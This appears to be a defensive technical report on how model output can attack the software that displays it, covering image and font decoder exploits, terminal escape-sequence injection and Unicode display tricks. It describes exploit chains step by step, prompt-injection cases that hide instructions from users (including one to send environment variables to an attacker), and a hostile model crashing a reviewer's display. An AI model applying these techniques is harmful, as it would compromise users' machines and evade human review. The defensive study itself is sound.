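Any digital circuit can be built from NAND gates alone. NSO used over 70,000 drawing commands to build a small computer inside the decoder, with registers and a 64-bit adder, and ran the next stage of the attack on it. An attacker can therefore run computations through a format that has no scripting if its decoder has a memory bug.

NSO used another image format, WebP, in a 2023 attack called BLASTPASS. WebP's lossless version uses Huffman coding, which gives frequent values short codes and rare values longer ones. To read these codes quickly, the library libwebp builds five lookup tables in one buffer. Its developers had worked out the maximum size of the tables for valid codes, but libwebp didn't check that the codes were valid until after it had written the tables.

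Isosceles' *The WebP 0day* (2023) shows how to trigger the flaw, CVE-2023-4863. The file needs four valid tables of the largest possible size and a fifth that is invalid in a particular way, so that it runs past the end of the buffer. Apparently the buffer sizes were right for valid tables, and the check for invalid ones came too late. Isosceles reproduced the sizes with a slightly modified version of a published tool, then tried every valid set of codes for the smallest table and found none that exceeded its allotted space. NVD's *CVE-2023-5129*, a withdrawn duplicate entry, instead attributes the flaw to buffer sizes that left out part of the tables.

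Beer (2025) explains in *An analysis of the NSO BLASTPASS iMessage exploit* that the flaw itself let the attackers write only one four-byte value, with almost no control over its contents, before the decoder detected the error and stopped. The compressed picture took up only 1,052 bytes of the 5.5 MB file. Nearly all the rest was metadata that made the phone reserve almost half a million blocks of memory in a precise arrangement. The file also contained the correct randomized memory addresses for the target's phone, which Beer thinks the attackers had obtained earlier through HomeKit, Apple's home automation system.

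Apple released its fix on 7 September 2023, and Google fixed Chrome five days later. Cloudflare's *Uncovering the Hidden WebP vulnerability* (2023) points out that nearly every application that handles WebP uses libwebp, so many other developers had to update too.

Apple fixed another exploited flaw in ImageIO, CVE-2025-43300, on 20 August 2025. It affected DNG, a format for unprocessed photographs, which can contain data compressed as lossless JPEG. The DNG file and the JPEG data inside it each record how many values a pixel has. Quarkslab's *Patch analysis of Apple iOS CVE-2025-43300* (2025) traces the flaw to files in which the DNG recorded two values and the JPEG data recorded one. The decoder assumed at least two values per pixel when it calculated how much to write in each row, so it wrote past the end of its buffer. The fix added a check on the position before the next write.

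According to OSV's *CVE-2025-43300* (2025), Apple had a report that this flaw may have been used in an "extremely sophisticated attack against specific targeted individuals". Attackers may have combined it with a WhatsApp flaw that could make a target's device download a file from any address and process it.

In January 2026, Project Zero published an attack that took over a Google Pixel 9 through its Dolby audio decoder, where an integer overflow again led to a buffer that was too small. Google Messages decoded incoming audio automatically to transcribe it, so the recipient did not have to play anything. Software that prepares attachments for an AI feature can therefore expose a decoder that an attacker could otherwise reach only if the user opened the file.

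### Why fonts are a special case

A font file contains tables that match characters to glyphs, tables of rules for arranging glyphs, and tables of glyph shapes, as *Memory safety for web fonts* (Röttsches, Sheeter and Brokaw, 2025) describes. Many fonts also include hinting instructions, small programs that adjust a shape to the screen's pixels so that it stays legible at small sizes. In some formats, the glyph itself is a program that draws curves. The font engine runs both kinds of program in an interpreter.

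An attacker who supplies a font therefore supplies a program too. That program can normally access only the font's own data, but a memory bug can remove that limit.

The spyware Duqu used such a font in 2011. Windows processed fonts in its kernel, the core of the operating system, which has full control of the machine. NVD's *CVE-2011-3402* records that a Word document or a web page could deliver the font. Teblin (2012), in *Anatomy of Duqu exploit*, explains the attack in a few steps:

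1. The font included small bitmap pictures of glyphs. Windows reserved a buffer for them but did not check that the position it wrote to was inside the buffer. The font's values put that position at more than five times the buffer's size.
2. The misplaced write increased the recorded size of a table that hinting programs are allowed to change.
3. The font's hinting program could now write beyond the real end of the table. It replaced the address of a function in the font engine.
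4. The program's next instruction made the engine use that address, and the attacker's code ran in the kernel.

Exploits written for targeted attacks can later be used in widespread ones. Wolf's *CVE-2011-3402 Technical Analysis* reports that the complete Duqu font later appeared in several kits that criminals use to infect large numbers of computers. The criminals could copy the file without understanding its hinting program.

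Teblin listed Firefox, Chrome, Safari and Adobe Reader as having protection against malicious fonts, but not Internet Explorer, Opera or Microsoft Office.

A more recent flaw affected FreeType, a font library that Chrome has used on Android, ChromeOS and Linux. According to GCVE's *CVE-2025-27363* (2025), versions up to 2.13.0 copied a 16-bit number that could be negative into a larger type that cannot hold negative numbers. A value of −1 became the largest possible number, and adding 4 gave 3. FreeType used the result to reserve a buffer that was too small and wrote up to six numbers outside it.

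Facebook assigned *CVE-2025-27363* to a flaw in FreeType, according to OSV. The record was published in March 2025 with a warning that attackers might already have used the flaw, and CISA's assessment lists exploitation as active. FreeType versions after 2.13.0 did not have the flaw, so the danger was in products that still contained an old copy.

### What a model's output can reach

Most of these attacks required the attacker to choose a file's exact bytes. A model's output may or may not give an attacker that much control.

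| Content | What its author controls | Code it reaches |
|---|---|---|
| Text in an installed font | The characters | Text shaping and the drawing of glyphs |
| Remote image | The whole file, at display time | Image decoders |
| Image in a data address | The whole file | Image decoders |
| SVG drawing | All of the markup | Drawing code and the decoders for anything embedded |
| Picture from an image generator | Roughly what it shows | An image decoder, with an ordinary file |
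| File written by an agent's code | The whole file | Any program that opens or previews it |

With plain text in an installed font, the adversary can choose characters but cannot add a hinting program or a faulty table. This rules out the Duqu and FreeType attacks. (A font supplied by an attacker can also draw misleading letters, which is a failure of faithful display.)

The text-shaping engine still has to process whatever characters arrive, and some sequences have crashed phones. In May 2015, a short message that included Arabic characters restarted iPhones when the phone shortened it to fit in a notification. In February 2018, a single cluster of characters in Telugu, a language of southern India, crashed apps on iPhones and Macs. Apple described that flaw as heap corruption, meaning it damaged memory the program was using.

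A sanitiser would have allowed both messages, because neither contained markup. An attacker could send them without compromising anything, and a model can write such characters as easily as any others. An app that reopens the same conversation may crash again, which can make recovery awkward. But both cases became known as crashes rather than as ways to run code. Arranging memory for a full exploit is probably much harder when the attacker can choose only characters.

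A data URL, which begins with `data:`, gives the adversary far more control because it contains a whole encoded file instead of the file's location. The browser decodes the file without contacting a server, so a ban on outbound requests does not stop the attack. A CSP can, because `img-src 'self'` blocks images in data URLs unless the developer also lists `data:`.

The picture in the BLASTPASS file that triggers the bug is 1,052 bytes, or 1,404 characters in base64, so it would fit in a chat answer. The complete 5.5 MB file would not fit, because it would need about 7.3 million characters. An answer would therefore have to leave out the data that arranged memory to make the bug useful on an iPhone. Other content in a chat window might arrange memory instead, but an attacker would have to design this for the particular browser.

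The model would also have to write the encoded file without errors. In the libwebp attack, one wrong bit makes the decoder reject the image harmlessly. Copying a prepared file from a web page is easier for a model than composing one, and an agent that can run code can avoid the problem by generating the file with a program.

SVG describes drawings in text, so the model can write shapes, gradients and filters directly, without any encoding. A drawing can also embed images in data URLs. An image generator gives the model less control over the file, because the model describes a picture and ordinary software encodes it.

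File attachments are the most exposed, because documents can embed images and fonts. Teblin lists Word, Excel, PowerPoint, PDF and email files among the formats that can carry a font. An exploit may run without the user opening the file if the file manager draws a thumbnail or a search tool indexes it. Even if a chat company secures its own chat window, it can still give the user a document that exploits another program.

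### Input that hangs the renderer

Some input stops a renderer without overwriting any memory. A picture with one colour compresses to a small file at almost any size, but its pixels do not stay small. At four bytes per pixel, an image of 50,000 by 50,000 pixels needs

50,000 × 50,000 × 4 = 10 billion bytes.

A drawing can also refer to a shape twice, group the two copies, refer to that group twice, and so on. After 30 steps, the renderer has to draw 2³⁰ (about 1.07 billion) shapes from a few lines of markup. Deeply nested lists or quotations can slow a badly written Markdown parser in a similar way.

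Developers can limit the number of pixels, the depth of nesting, and the time and memory that each answer may use. The renderer should apply these limits to the decoded content, because file size is a poor predictor of how much work the file will cause.

A crash or a hang leaks nothing by itself, but it can keep people from judging a model's output. A hostile model could make an incriminating answer impossible to open, and a review system that skips items after an error would let that answer through. The system should instead treat the failure as a reason to inspect the item more closely.

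### Relying on unknown flaws staying unknown

Developers look for decoder bugs mainly by fuzzing, which means automatically running a program on huge numbers of altered files. Fuzzing finds many bugs, but Google's OSS-Fuzz project did not find the one in libwebp despite testing the lossless decoder extensively. Random changes are very unlikely to produce four valid tables of the right size followed by a suitable invalid one. After the fix, Google released a fuzzer specifically for the Huffman code, but it still did not find the flaw when Isosceles ran it for a while on the old version.

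Fonts are hard to fuzz for similar reasons. Röttsches and colleagues explain that a font's tables depend on each other, so a random change to one usually makes the engine reject the file before the deeper code runs. One serious flaw in FreeType's support for colour fonts took more than ten months to find. Google needed at least a quarter of one engineer's time to keep up with the bugs that fuzzing did find.

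Isosceles suspects that someone found the libwebp flaw by reading the code, and that most reviewers would have given up too early. If so, the flaw stayed hidden partly because few people had the skill and patience to look for it.

AI systems are changing that. In February 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Opus 4.6 had found a flaw in CGIF, a library that writes GIF images. CGIF's developers had assumed that compressed data would never be larger than the original, but GIF's compression method can make some images grow. In April, Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos Preview had found a 16-year-old flaw in a video decoder in FFmpeg, a widely used media library. Both reports are Anthropic's accounts of its own models, and finding a flaw is easier than building a working attack like BLASTPASS. Still, finding the CGIF flaw required an understanding of the format, and ordinary fuzzing is weakest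 on flaws of that kind.

Developers can use the same systems to find and fix flaws before attackers do. But users benefit only after updating, and attackers can study a published fix to find the flaw it repaired. The FreeType flaw was still dangerous in 2025 even though newer versions of the library no longer had it.

A clean record is therefore weaker evidence than it used to be that a decoder is safe to use on untrusted model output. If the model is the adversary, it might even look for a flaw in the display software, much of which is open source.

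### Memory-safe rewrites

Rewriting the software in a memory-safe language can remove the whole class of bug. In Rust, for example, ordinary code checks each buffer access and stops the program in a controlled way if the access is out of range. A wrong length in the file then does not make the program write outside the buffer.

Google has developed Skrifa, a font library in Rust, to replace FreeType in Chrome. Röttsches and colleagues report about 700 tests of its code. They also compared its output with FreeType's to check that text still looked right. From June 2024 to March 2025, fuzzing found 39 bugs in Skrifa and the code that connects it to Chrome. None was security-critical, but some caused wrong shapes or controlled crashes.

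This is good evidence for the rewrite, but the same fuzzing methods do not easily reach deep font code, so finding no serious flaw does not prove that none exists. Rust itself is the stronger reason for confidence. It does allow code marked "unsafe", which lacks some of the language's protections, but Skrifa's developers avoided writing such code and left the one operation that required it to a separate, widely tested library.

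Skrifa replaces the code that reads a font's measurements and shapes. The characters in an answer also pass through the shaping engine, so Skrifa alone does not prevent crashes like those in 2015 and 2018. Google introduced it gradually, starting with less common web font formats and leaving system fonts for later.

### Sandboxed decoding

Developers can also run the decoder in a sandbox, which limits which files, services and other processes it can use. An attacker who takes over the decoder then needs a second flaw to escape.

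Apple introduced a sandbox called BlastDoor for incoming iMessages, but FORCEDENTRY avoided it because iMessage handled GIFs in another process with looser restrictions. The attackers escaped from that process without further memory corruption. They sent a specially constructed object to a telephone service, which evaluated an expression inside it as a program (Beer and Groß, 2022). Because the service used its normal functions, signed addresses and similar memory protections could not stop this, and a rewrite in Rust would not necessarily have stopped it either.

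Apple moved all GIF decoding into BlastDoor with iOS 15 in September 2021. Beer found that the BLASTPASS attack files he examined ran inside BlastDoor, though Isosceles had initially thought that BLASTPASS avoided it too. The attackers had encrypted the next stage, which probably contained an escape, and sent the key in a separate message, which Beer never recovered. He found signs in later crash logs that the image could also reach the decoder outside BlastDoor.

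The sandbox evidently made the attack longer and harder, but it did not protect the target. A sandbox protects only what is outside it, so it helps little if the sandboxed process also holds the conversation or draws the rest of the page.

Firefox's RLBox system isolates some libraries more finely, confining each to its own region of memory inside the browser's process. Firefox has to check the values that these libraries return. RLBox has covered the Graphite font engine, among others, since Firefox 95, released in December 2021. A bug in Graphite can still corrupt Graphite's own data and draw the wrong text, but it should not give an attacker control of the browser.

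Google requires a sandbox when code in an unsafe language processes untrusted data. One aim of rewriting its font code in Rust, according to *Upcoming roll-out plans for the Rust-based secure font stack in Blink*, is to allow font tasks to run outside the sandbox. That is reasonable for speed, but a renderer for output from a possibly hostile model should use both Rust and a sandbox, because each protects against failures that the other does not.

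### Accepting fewer formats

Neither a rewrite nor a sandbox reduces the number of formats that an attacker can send. Beer concludes that developers should first find out how much code incoming data can reach, then reduce that amount. He points out that both NSO attacks sent files with misleading extensions: a PDF as a `.gif` in FORCEDENTRY and a WebP image as a `.png` in BLASTPASS.

Apple restricted the formats that iMessage's GIF process could decode in October 2021. Its Lockdown Mode extends the same approach to other parts of the phone. A chat service can restrict formats more easily than a general messaging app, since it probably needs only PNG and JPEG. It should check that each file's contents match a permitted format and call that format's decoder directly, because a library that detects the format automatically may use a decoder that the service did not mean to support.

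A chat window that displays only text does not need an image decoder. It still needs a font engine and a shaping engine, but the developer can block web fonts and use a small set of installed ones. The model's output then determines only the characters.

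## Control sequences in terminals

A terminal is the text window in which programmers type commands and read the results. Many coding agents run in terminals, and administrators read logs there. A terminal prints most of the characters it receives but treats some as instructions, called control sequences. Text that would be harmless in a chat window can therefore erase the screen, change the clipboard or, in some terminals, run a program.

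### One stream for text and commands

Early terminals such as teletypes were machines that printed the text sent to them. Leadbeater (2023), in *Terminally Owned*, dates both the ASCII character code and one of the first devices to use it, the Teletype Model 33, to 1963. Commands such as ringing the bell or returning to the start of the line had to arrive over the same connection as the text, so ASCII reserves 33 of its 128 codes for control characters. One of them is the escape character, code 27 (1B in hexadecimal).

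Digital Equipment Corporation later created longer commands for its VT series of video terminals. According to *Terminal Lucidity* (2025), a standard covers some of these commands, often called ANSI escape codes, and the vast majority begin with the escape character. Today's terminals are programs that imitate the old machines.

Suppose a program prints this line, where `{ESC}` stands for a single escape character:

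`Lunch is at {ESC}[32mnoon{ESC}[0m.`

When a terminal reads an escape character, it stops printing and starts to collect a command. In *Weaponizing Plain Text*, STÖK (2023) explains the parts of one such command, `ESC[32m`. The bracket introduces the sequence, 32 means green, and the m ends the sequence and marks it as a text style. The terminal then prints "noon" in green, and a second sequence restores the normal style. The terminal would do the same if a stranger had written the line, because the stream contains no record of who added a sequence.

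Programs that read files often pass control sequences to the terminal unchanged. STÖK lists `cat`, `grep`, `tail` and `awk` as examples, all common commands for reading logs. A text editor instead shows the sequences as visible codes. Sequences can also reach a terminal by accident. *Terminal Lucidity* cites questions from users whose terminals became unreadable after they displayed a binary file.

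### What the sequences can do

| Effect | Property it breaks | Restrictions |
|---|---|---|
| Moves the cursor, overwrites or erases text | Faithful display | Generally none, because ordinary programs need it |
| Colours or conceals text | Faithful display | Generally none |
| Sets the window title | Faithful display, if the title is misleading | Generally none |
| Creates a link whose text differs from its address | Faithful display, and no outbound requests if the user clicks | Apple's Terminal does not make such links clickable, and Visual Studio Code asks before it opens one |
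| Writes to the clipboard | No exploitable parsing | Many terminals remove a final newline, so that pasting does not run a command |
| Reads the clipboard | No exploitable parsing | Few terminals support it. Debian, Red Hat and OpenBSD turn it off in xterm |
| Names a host when setting the working directory | No outbound requests | Depends on whether the terminal looks up the host |
| Makes the terminal send a reply | No exploitable parsing | Nearly all terminals refuse to report their title by default, but other replies remain |

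A terminal that changes the clipboard is working as designed, but it fails the second property because it does more than display text. Terminals also have ordinary memory bugs. In xterm, a command for repeating part of a picture lacked a bounds check until 2022, so one short line of text could crash the program.

The working-directory sequence lets a new tab open in the same folder as the old one. Apple's Terminal accepts the folder as a URL that can include a host name, and it looks up that name to check whether it belongs to the user's own computer. As with some prefetch hints, the lookup can send data in the host name to an attacker without a click.

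### Text that the user does not see

*Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (Trail of Bits, April 2025) reported that Claude Code version 0.2.76 did not filter control sequences in the descriptions and output of MCP tools. Trail of Bits, a security company, built malicious tools that used these sequences to hide instructions from the user.

One tool returned a description of the user's computers that included an instruction to download Python from a particular server, written in white on the terminal's default background. The user saw only the harmless sentences around it, but the model read the full text and recommended the attacker's server. The trick fails on a dark background, where white text is readable.

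Moving the cursor avoids that problem. In another example, the text began with an instruction to send the user's environment variables to an attacker, then moved the cursor back up and overwrote the instruction with a fake report of a successful security scan. A longer example cleared the screen and added blank lines, so the window seemed to have scrolled.

Trail of Bits tested only one early version of Claude Code. Users can check a later version, or another agent, by having it display a file containing a harmless colour sequence. If the colour appears, the agent is passing on sequences from the file.

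Programs without a model can have the same flaw. According to GCVE, a command-line tool for the chat server Mattermost printed users' posts unfiltered until a fix in March 2026, so a post could show an administrator a fake prompt or change the clipboard. GCVE's *CWE-150* also includes a 2025 flaw in a logging library written in Rust. Rust's memory safety did not prevent it because the library copied the characters correctly.

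Dangerzone converts risky documents into safe PDFs inside an isolated container. Before version 0.4.2, its command-line interface logged the container's output to the user's terminal without neutralising escape characters, according to Vulners' *CVE-2023-39342 Dangerzone CLI does not sanitize ANSI escape characters*. A document that took over the container could therefore have sent escape characters to the terminal outside it.

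### Replies that the shell reads as typing

Some control sequences request information from the terminal, such as the cursor's position. The terminal sends its reply through the same channel as the user's keystrokes. If the program that sent the request is no longer reading input, the reply goes to the shell, the program that runs typed commands.

*Terminal Emulator Security Issues* (H D Moore, Digital Defense, 2003) describes how an attacker could use text displayed in a terminal to run a command. The text set the window title to the command, then made the terminal report the title by writing it to the shell's input. It then made further output invisible and prompted the user to press Enter, which ran the command.

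In a follow-up on the Bugtraq mailing list, Moore (2003) reported that xterm, rxvt and PuTTY were vulnerable, but Konsole and GNOME Terminal 2.0 were not. By 2015, the library behind GNOME Terminal returned the same fixed title for every title request, and Chazelas (2015), in a mailing-list post, quoted a comment in its code warning never to report the real one. Yet in 2022 the original command worked unchanged in WezTerm, a much newer terminal. In ConEmu, a terminal for Windows, the reply could include control characters, so the command ran without the user pressing anything.

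Nguyen (2026), in *cat readme.txt" is not safe in iTerm2*, describes a new version of the problem in iTerm2, a terminal for Macs. OpenAI's Codex found the flaw, which works as follows:

1. When a user connects to another computer, iTerm2 can start a helper script there. The two communicate through control sequences in the ordinary text stream.
2. A malicious text file contains the sequences that such a helper would send. When the user displays the file, iTerm2 takes them for a real helper.
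3. iTerm2 sends encoded commands to the helper. No helper is running, so the user's own shell receives them as typed input.
4. Most of them fail as nonsense. The attacker has chosen the file's contents so that the last piece is also a valid path to a program, and the shell runs that program if it exists.

The attack works only if the attacker's program is in the right place under the current folder. An archive containing both files meets this condition once the user unpacks it there. Nguyen's team reported the flaw on 30 March. iTerm2's developer fixed the source code the next day, but the fix had not reached a stable release by 17 April. NVD's *CVE-2026-41253* (2026) lists iTerm2 versions up to 3.6.9 as affected. The team also rebuilt a working exploit from the published fix alone.

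Leadbeater's tool vt-houdini tests terminals for known flaws. *Terminal Emulator Security* (2026) reports that the versions of Kitty and Konsole in Debian's Trixie release passed. Such tests catch old flaws that reappear, as happened in WezTerm, but they would not have caught the iTerm2 flaw, which was new.

### Getting a model to emit escape characters

In November 2024, Leon Derczynski reported that many language models can output the escape character itself. Rehberger followed this up in Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* with a small command-line program that sent a file or web page to a preview version of GPT-4o and printed the answer. When a user asked for a summary of a malicious file, the model followed the file's instructions and emitted sequences that made the terminal beep and flash. A web page made the model emit sequences that moved the cursor and cleared the screen.

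Rehberger also put data from the model's input into a clickable link and wrote text to the clipboard, which could lead to code running in certain terminals. He used Google's Gemini to leak data through the host lookup in Apple's Terminal. Gemini could run code, which produced the necessary characters more reliably than the model did by writing them directly. Rehberger found that models can also read control characters, so an attacker can supply a finished sequence and ask the model to repeat it. He gave no success rates, and some demonstrations took several attempts.

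garak, an open-source tool that tests models for vulnerabilities, now has three tests for this. The first tries to make a model output raw sequences, with a real escape character. The second looks for written-out forms such as `\x1b`, which consists of four ordinary characters. The third searches the model's vocabulary for tokens that contain escape sequences.

AVID (2026), a public database of AI vulnerabilities, records that Moonshot AI's Kimi-K2-Instruct-0905 failed 6 of 58 attempts (about 10%) on the raw test, and Essential AI's rnj-1-instruct failed 12 of 58 (about 21%). On the written-out test, rnj-1-instruct failed 36 of 51 attempts (71%, calculated from the passes AVID reports). This last figure overstates the danger, because a terminal prints `\x1b` as four characters unless another program decodes it first, and any answer that explains terminal colours has to include something like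 it.

A test prompt may ask the model to repeat a string, as an example in Mindgard's *AnsiEscaped* does. The results therefore show what models can do on request more than how often they follow a third party's instructions. If the model itself is the adversary, its ability is what matters, and even the lower failure rate is too high to trust its output.

In *Training a General Purpose Automated Red Teaming Model*, Padmakumar, Derczynski and colleagues (2026) trained a small model, Qwen3-8B, to write prompts that make other models misbehave. For each goal, a larger model supplied examples, ways to disguise the request, and criteria for success. The small model wrote attacks, a target model answered them, and a judge model applied the criteria. Reinforcement learning rewarded successful attacks. The training covered 15 goals, mostly offensive content. The researchers kept six goals for the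 final test, including raw escape sequences, and used garak's detectors to determine which attacks succeeded.

The researchers chose their main trained version by its results on the training goals. On the other six goals, it succeeded in 29.35% of attempts on average, compared with 20.87% for the untrained model. Another version, trained with Qwen3-8B as the target, succeeded in 37.8% on these goals. The averages also cover malware and code that imports non-existent packages, so they do not measure success on escape sequences alone. In an earlier experiment, the researchers trained the model only on escape sequences, which typically raised its success rate too. They caution that the behaviour they elicited was not always dangerous in itself. For example, sequences that only format text are typically less of a problem than some others.

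MITRE's *CWE-150*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives its highest rating to neutralising escape codes before they reach the terminal. It rates removing the codes from a model's vocabulary as of limited effectiveness, because the model may still assemble a sequence from several tokens.

### Making control characters visible

The program that prints the model's output should first replace every control character except newline and tab with a visible notation. Rehberger uses caret notation, which writes a control character as a caret followed by the character whose code is 64 higher. Escape (code 27) becomes `^[` because `[` has code 91, and backspace (code 8) becomes `^H`. Delete (code 127) is an exception, written as `^?`.

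Consider this line, where `{BS}` is a backspace:

`Lunch is at noon{BS}{BS}{BS}{BS}{ESC}[32mone.{ESC}[0m`

A terminal moves back four places, overwrites "noon", and shows "Lunch is at one." with the last word in green. After the replacement, it shows everything:

`Lunch is at noon^H^H^H^H^[[32mone.^[[0m`

Trail of Bits recommends the simpler rule of replacing only the escape character. With a question mark as the replacement, the terminal would show `Lunch is at ?[32mone.?[0m`. The colour no longer works, but the backspaces still hide "noon". Unicode also has a second set of control characters, codes 128 to 159, one of which does the same job as an escape character followed by a bracket. In 2023, Kitty, WezTerm and terminals based on GNOME's library accepted this character by default.

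MITRE suggests allowing printable characters and selected whitespace, such as the carriage return. But a carriage return moves the cursor to the start of the line, so the text after it can overwrite what is already there. A strict rule has to replace carriage returns too.

Deleting control characters is worse than replacing them. MITRE lists an application that removed escape sequences from a file name in its approval dialog but kept them in the name it used, so the user could approve access to the wrong file. Deletion also requires the filter to recognise where each sequence ends. Documentation for a Go library on pkg.go.dev warns that some sequences end in characters such as `@` or `~`, and that filters that only match sequences ending in a letter leave these behind. Replacing control characters one at a time avoids this problem and works on output that is still arriving, provided the program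 decodes the bytes into characters first.

The rule must cover everything the agent displays, including tool output, file names and error messages. An application that uses colour should replace the control characters first and add its own colour sequences afterwards. It can then show `^[` in a reserved colour when it stands for an escape character, so that readers can distinguish it from a caret and a bracket that the model wrote. Invisible and reordering Unicode characters still get through, because Unicode does not class them as control characters.

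### What stops working

Progress bars usually redraw themselves by returning to the start of the line, so under this rule each update appears after the last one, separated by `^M`. Text files from Windows show the same `^M` at the end of every line. Coloured output from compilers and file comparisons is full of codes such as `^[[32m`. An agent can avoid most of this by running its tools with colour and progress bars turned off. It can then colour comparisons itself, since added and removed lines begin with a plus or minus sign.

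Full-screen programs such as text editors cannot work under the rule. An agent could run them in an in-memory terminal emulator and print only the characters on the resulting screen. This keeps their sequences away from the user's terminal, but loses any text the program has overwritten or concealed, so the method does not suit someone checking what the model wrote.

Anyone inspecting untrusted output in a terminal has to choose viewing tools carefully. The program `less`, which git uses by default to display code changes, interprets backspaces and can hide text in a change. `cat -v` shows control characters in caret notation, but it also turns accented letters into codes. A GNU tool gives more detail by listing each control character by its name and key combination, so a backspace appears as "BS" and "Control-H".

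## When the display differs from the underlying bytes

A viewer that does not execute control sequences can still mislead its reader, because many different byte strings look the same on screen.

### Faithful display as a function

For a given program, font and window, rendering is a function f that assigns a picture to every string of bytes. Faithful display then means:

if a ≠ b, then f(a) ≠ f(b).

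Two pictures count as the same if the viewer cannot tell them apart, even if a few pixels differ.

Ordinary rendering can make different strings look the same. The Latin letters c, o and a have Cyrillic counterparts that many fonts draw identically. Each letter of "cocoa" can come from either alphabet, so 2⁵ = 32 different strings can look like that word. Invisible characters make the number unlimited, because a writer can insert any number of them.

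A window of fixed size also cannot display all text faithfully. A window with 25 lines of 80 characters can show at most 95²⁰⁰⁰ different screens of printable ASCII, but the number of possible strings is unlimited. The viewer has to continue long text on further pages or show how much it has left out.

The difference matters when one party judges what is displayed and another party, or a program, acts on the bytes. For example, a reviewer approves code as it appears on screen, but the compiler translates the bytes. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) describes how, when a coding agent asks for permission, an operator can approve a different command from the one displayed. Electronic signatures raise the same problem. Lioy, Ramunno and colleagues point out in *Motivations for a theoretical approach to WYSIWYS* that signers never see the bits they sign, only one possible representation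 of them.

### Characters with no visible form

*Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) tested the 235 characters in Unicode's "Control" and "Format" categories in a terminal, a text document and a CSV file, and found 130 with no visible effect. Each of these can carry log₂ 130 ≈ 7 bits, enough to encode one ASCII character. Other programs may show some of them.

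Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* (2024) explains that Unicode's tag characters form an invisible copy of ASCII. When a reader of that blog opened a sample file in Chrome, the browser's inspection tool displayed three characters but reported 14 glyphs. WordPress appears to remove tag characters from the text it stores.

Language models can read text that people cannot see. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) tested whether five models follow instructions written in invisible characters, across two encodings and 8,308 outputs. Models complied far more often when they could use tools, and which encoding worked depended on the provider. A person may therefore approve an answer and pass it to another model without noticing that it contains instructions for that model.

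Line breaks can mislead too. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Source Code Handling* (2024) describes a C program with a comment on one line and a safety check on the next. If the break between them is a rare character called the line separator, an editor may show two lines, but the compiler treats both as one comment and skips the check.

Readers can sometimes find invisible characters by moving through the text with the arrow keys, because the cursor may seem to stay in place for a keystroke. A program that lists every character by its Unicode number is more reliable.

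### Right-to-left reordering

Computers store Hebrew and Arabic in reading order, like English, and the renderer uses the Unicode Bidirectional Algorithm to work out where each character belongs on the line. The algorithm cannot always infer the right order in mixed text, so Unicode also has invisible characters that set the direction. A writer can apply them to Latin letters, so that the stored text "abc" appears as "cba". By nesting these characters, a writer can make the stored text appear as almost any anagram of itself.

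*Trojan Source* (Boucher and Anderson, 2021) showed how attackers can use directional characters to deceive code reviewers. Most compilers reject these characters in ordinary code but accept them in comments and quoted strings. An editor applies them to the whole line, so part of a comment can look like code, and code can look like part of a comment. The attacker chooses an order in which the displayed text is also a valid program, so the reviewer sees nothing unusual.

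In one Python example, a function appears to subtract 50 from Alice's bank balance of 100. The word "return" appears to be part of the comment above that step, but Python executes it as a command, so the function ends early and the balance stays at 100.

Boucher and Anderson used directional characters to write programs in 12 languages that appeared to print nothing but in fact printed "You are an admin." Only Solidity, a language for blockchain contracts, had a defence, and its compiler rejected some directional characters but not others.

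They also tested ten editors and three code-hosting sites on up to three operating systems. Visual Studio Code and Atom showed the false order on all three systems, as did GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket in Chrome and Firefox. Sublime Text ignored the directional characters, and IntelliJ made them visible. Emacs showed the false order on Windows and Ubuntu but displayed underscores on macOS, so developers who test a viewer on one system cannot assume it behaves the same on another.

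Syntax highlighting, which colours comments differently from code, did not reliably expose the attack. Some editors coloured some attacks strangely, but an attacker could test several versions in the target's editor and choose the least conspicuous one.

### How the vendors responded

Boucher and Anderson began contacting 19 companies and organisations on 25 July 2021 and gave them 99 days before publication. Nine committed to a patch. Some recipients closed the report immediately because it did not resemble a familiar flaw. Reports that named a specific product at risk worked best. Eleven recipients had bug bounty programmes, and five of those paid an average of about $2,246.

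GitHub added a warning banner and began to show directional characters as codes. GitLab, Bitbucket and Visual Studio Code also made them visible, and Emacs now highlights suspicious uses. Rust's compiler now rejects the characters unless the programmer writes them as codes, while the GCC compiler issues a warning. The LLVM compiler project's developers put the check in a separate tool for performance reasons. The Java team considered the attack a problem for editors and did not change the language.

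The Unicode Consortium partly agrees with the Java team. These problems affect only code that people read, so a compiler that processes machine-generated code should not have to enforce complicated rules about appearance. Boucher and Anderson accept that the language is more at fault than the compiler, but they want compilers to check by default because that protects the most people. Their argument is stronger for code that a developer may view in several programs, since the attack can work if even one of those programs is unprotected.

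GitHub also looked for earlier attacks by searching more than a billion public commits (saved changes to code) from January to mid-October 2021 for unterminated directional characters. It found 7,444 matches. Boucher and Anderson classed 98.8% of them as false positives, such as badly formed strings in right-to-left languages. The rest included code deliberately made hard to read and experiments by two recipients of the confidential reports. A separate search of Rust's package collection found no attacks.

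Fewer than one commit in 130,000 matched, so most developers would rarely see a false warning. Developers who work with Hebrew or Arabic text would see more.

### Reordering without hidden characters

Reordering can change what text appears to mean even if the text contains no directional control characters. The Unicode Consortium gives the example of an Arabic sentence that begins with "YouTube", ends with "Google", and means that YouTube is a subsidiary of Google. It reads correctly in a right-to-left paragraph, but in a left-to-right paragraph the two names swap places and the sentence appears to mean that Google is a subsidiary of YouTube.

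A chat window that displays every paragraph from left to right could reverse a correct answer even without an attacker. Removing directional characters would not help, because the answer contains none.

### Look-alike letters

In July 2000, fraudsters registered the domain paypaI.com, with a capital I in place of the final l, to collect PayPal passwords. Both letters are ASCII, and Unicode has many more pairs of characters that look alike, called homoglyphs. According to *What You See Is Not Always What You Get* (2024), the Unicode Consortium publishes a list of characters that fonts are meant to draw with the same glyph. Readers cannot tell these characters apart by looking.

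The Unicode Consortium describes a C program that appears to set every number in a table to zero. It clears only the diagonal, because part of the program writes the variable i with a lookalike Cyrillic letter. Boucher and Anderson created two functions that both appeared to be named `sayHello`, one with a Cyrillic Н. The substitution worked in 10 of the 12 languages they tested. Two GNU compilers rejected their test program, and Rust's compiler warned about the mixed alphabets but still built it.

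Invisible characters in function names worked less well, because nearly all the compilers reported an error. After publication, other programmers pointed out that an invisible character can instead break up the symbol that ends a comment. The compiler then treats the code that follows as part of the comment.

Look-alikes also cause honest mistakes. A Russian programmer who names something `HTTPОтвет` ("HTTP response") has to switch keyboard layouts midway and may leave a Latin O in the Russian part. The compiler later reports that the name does not exist, although it seems to be on the screen.

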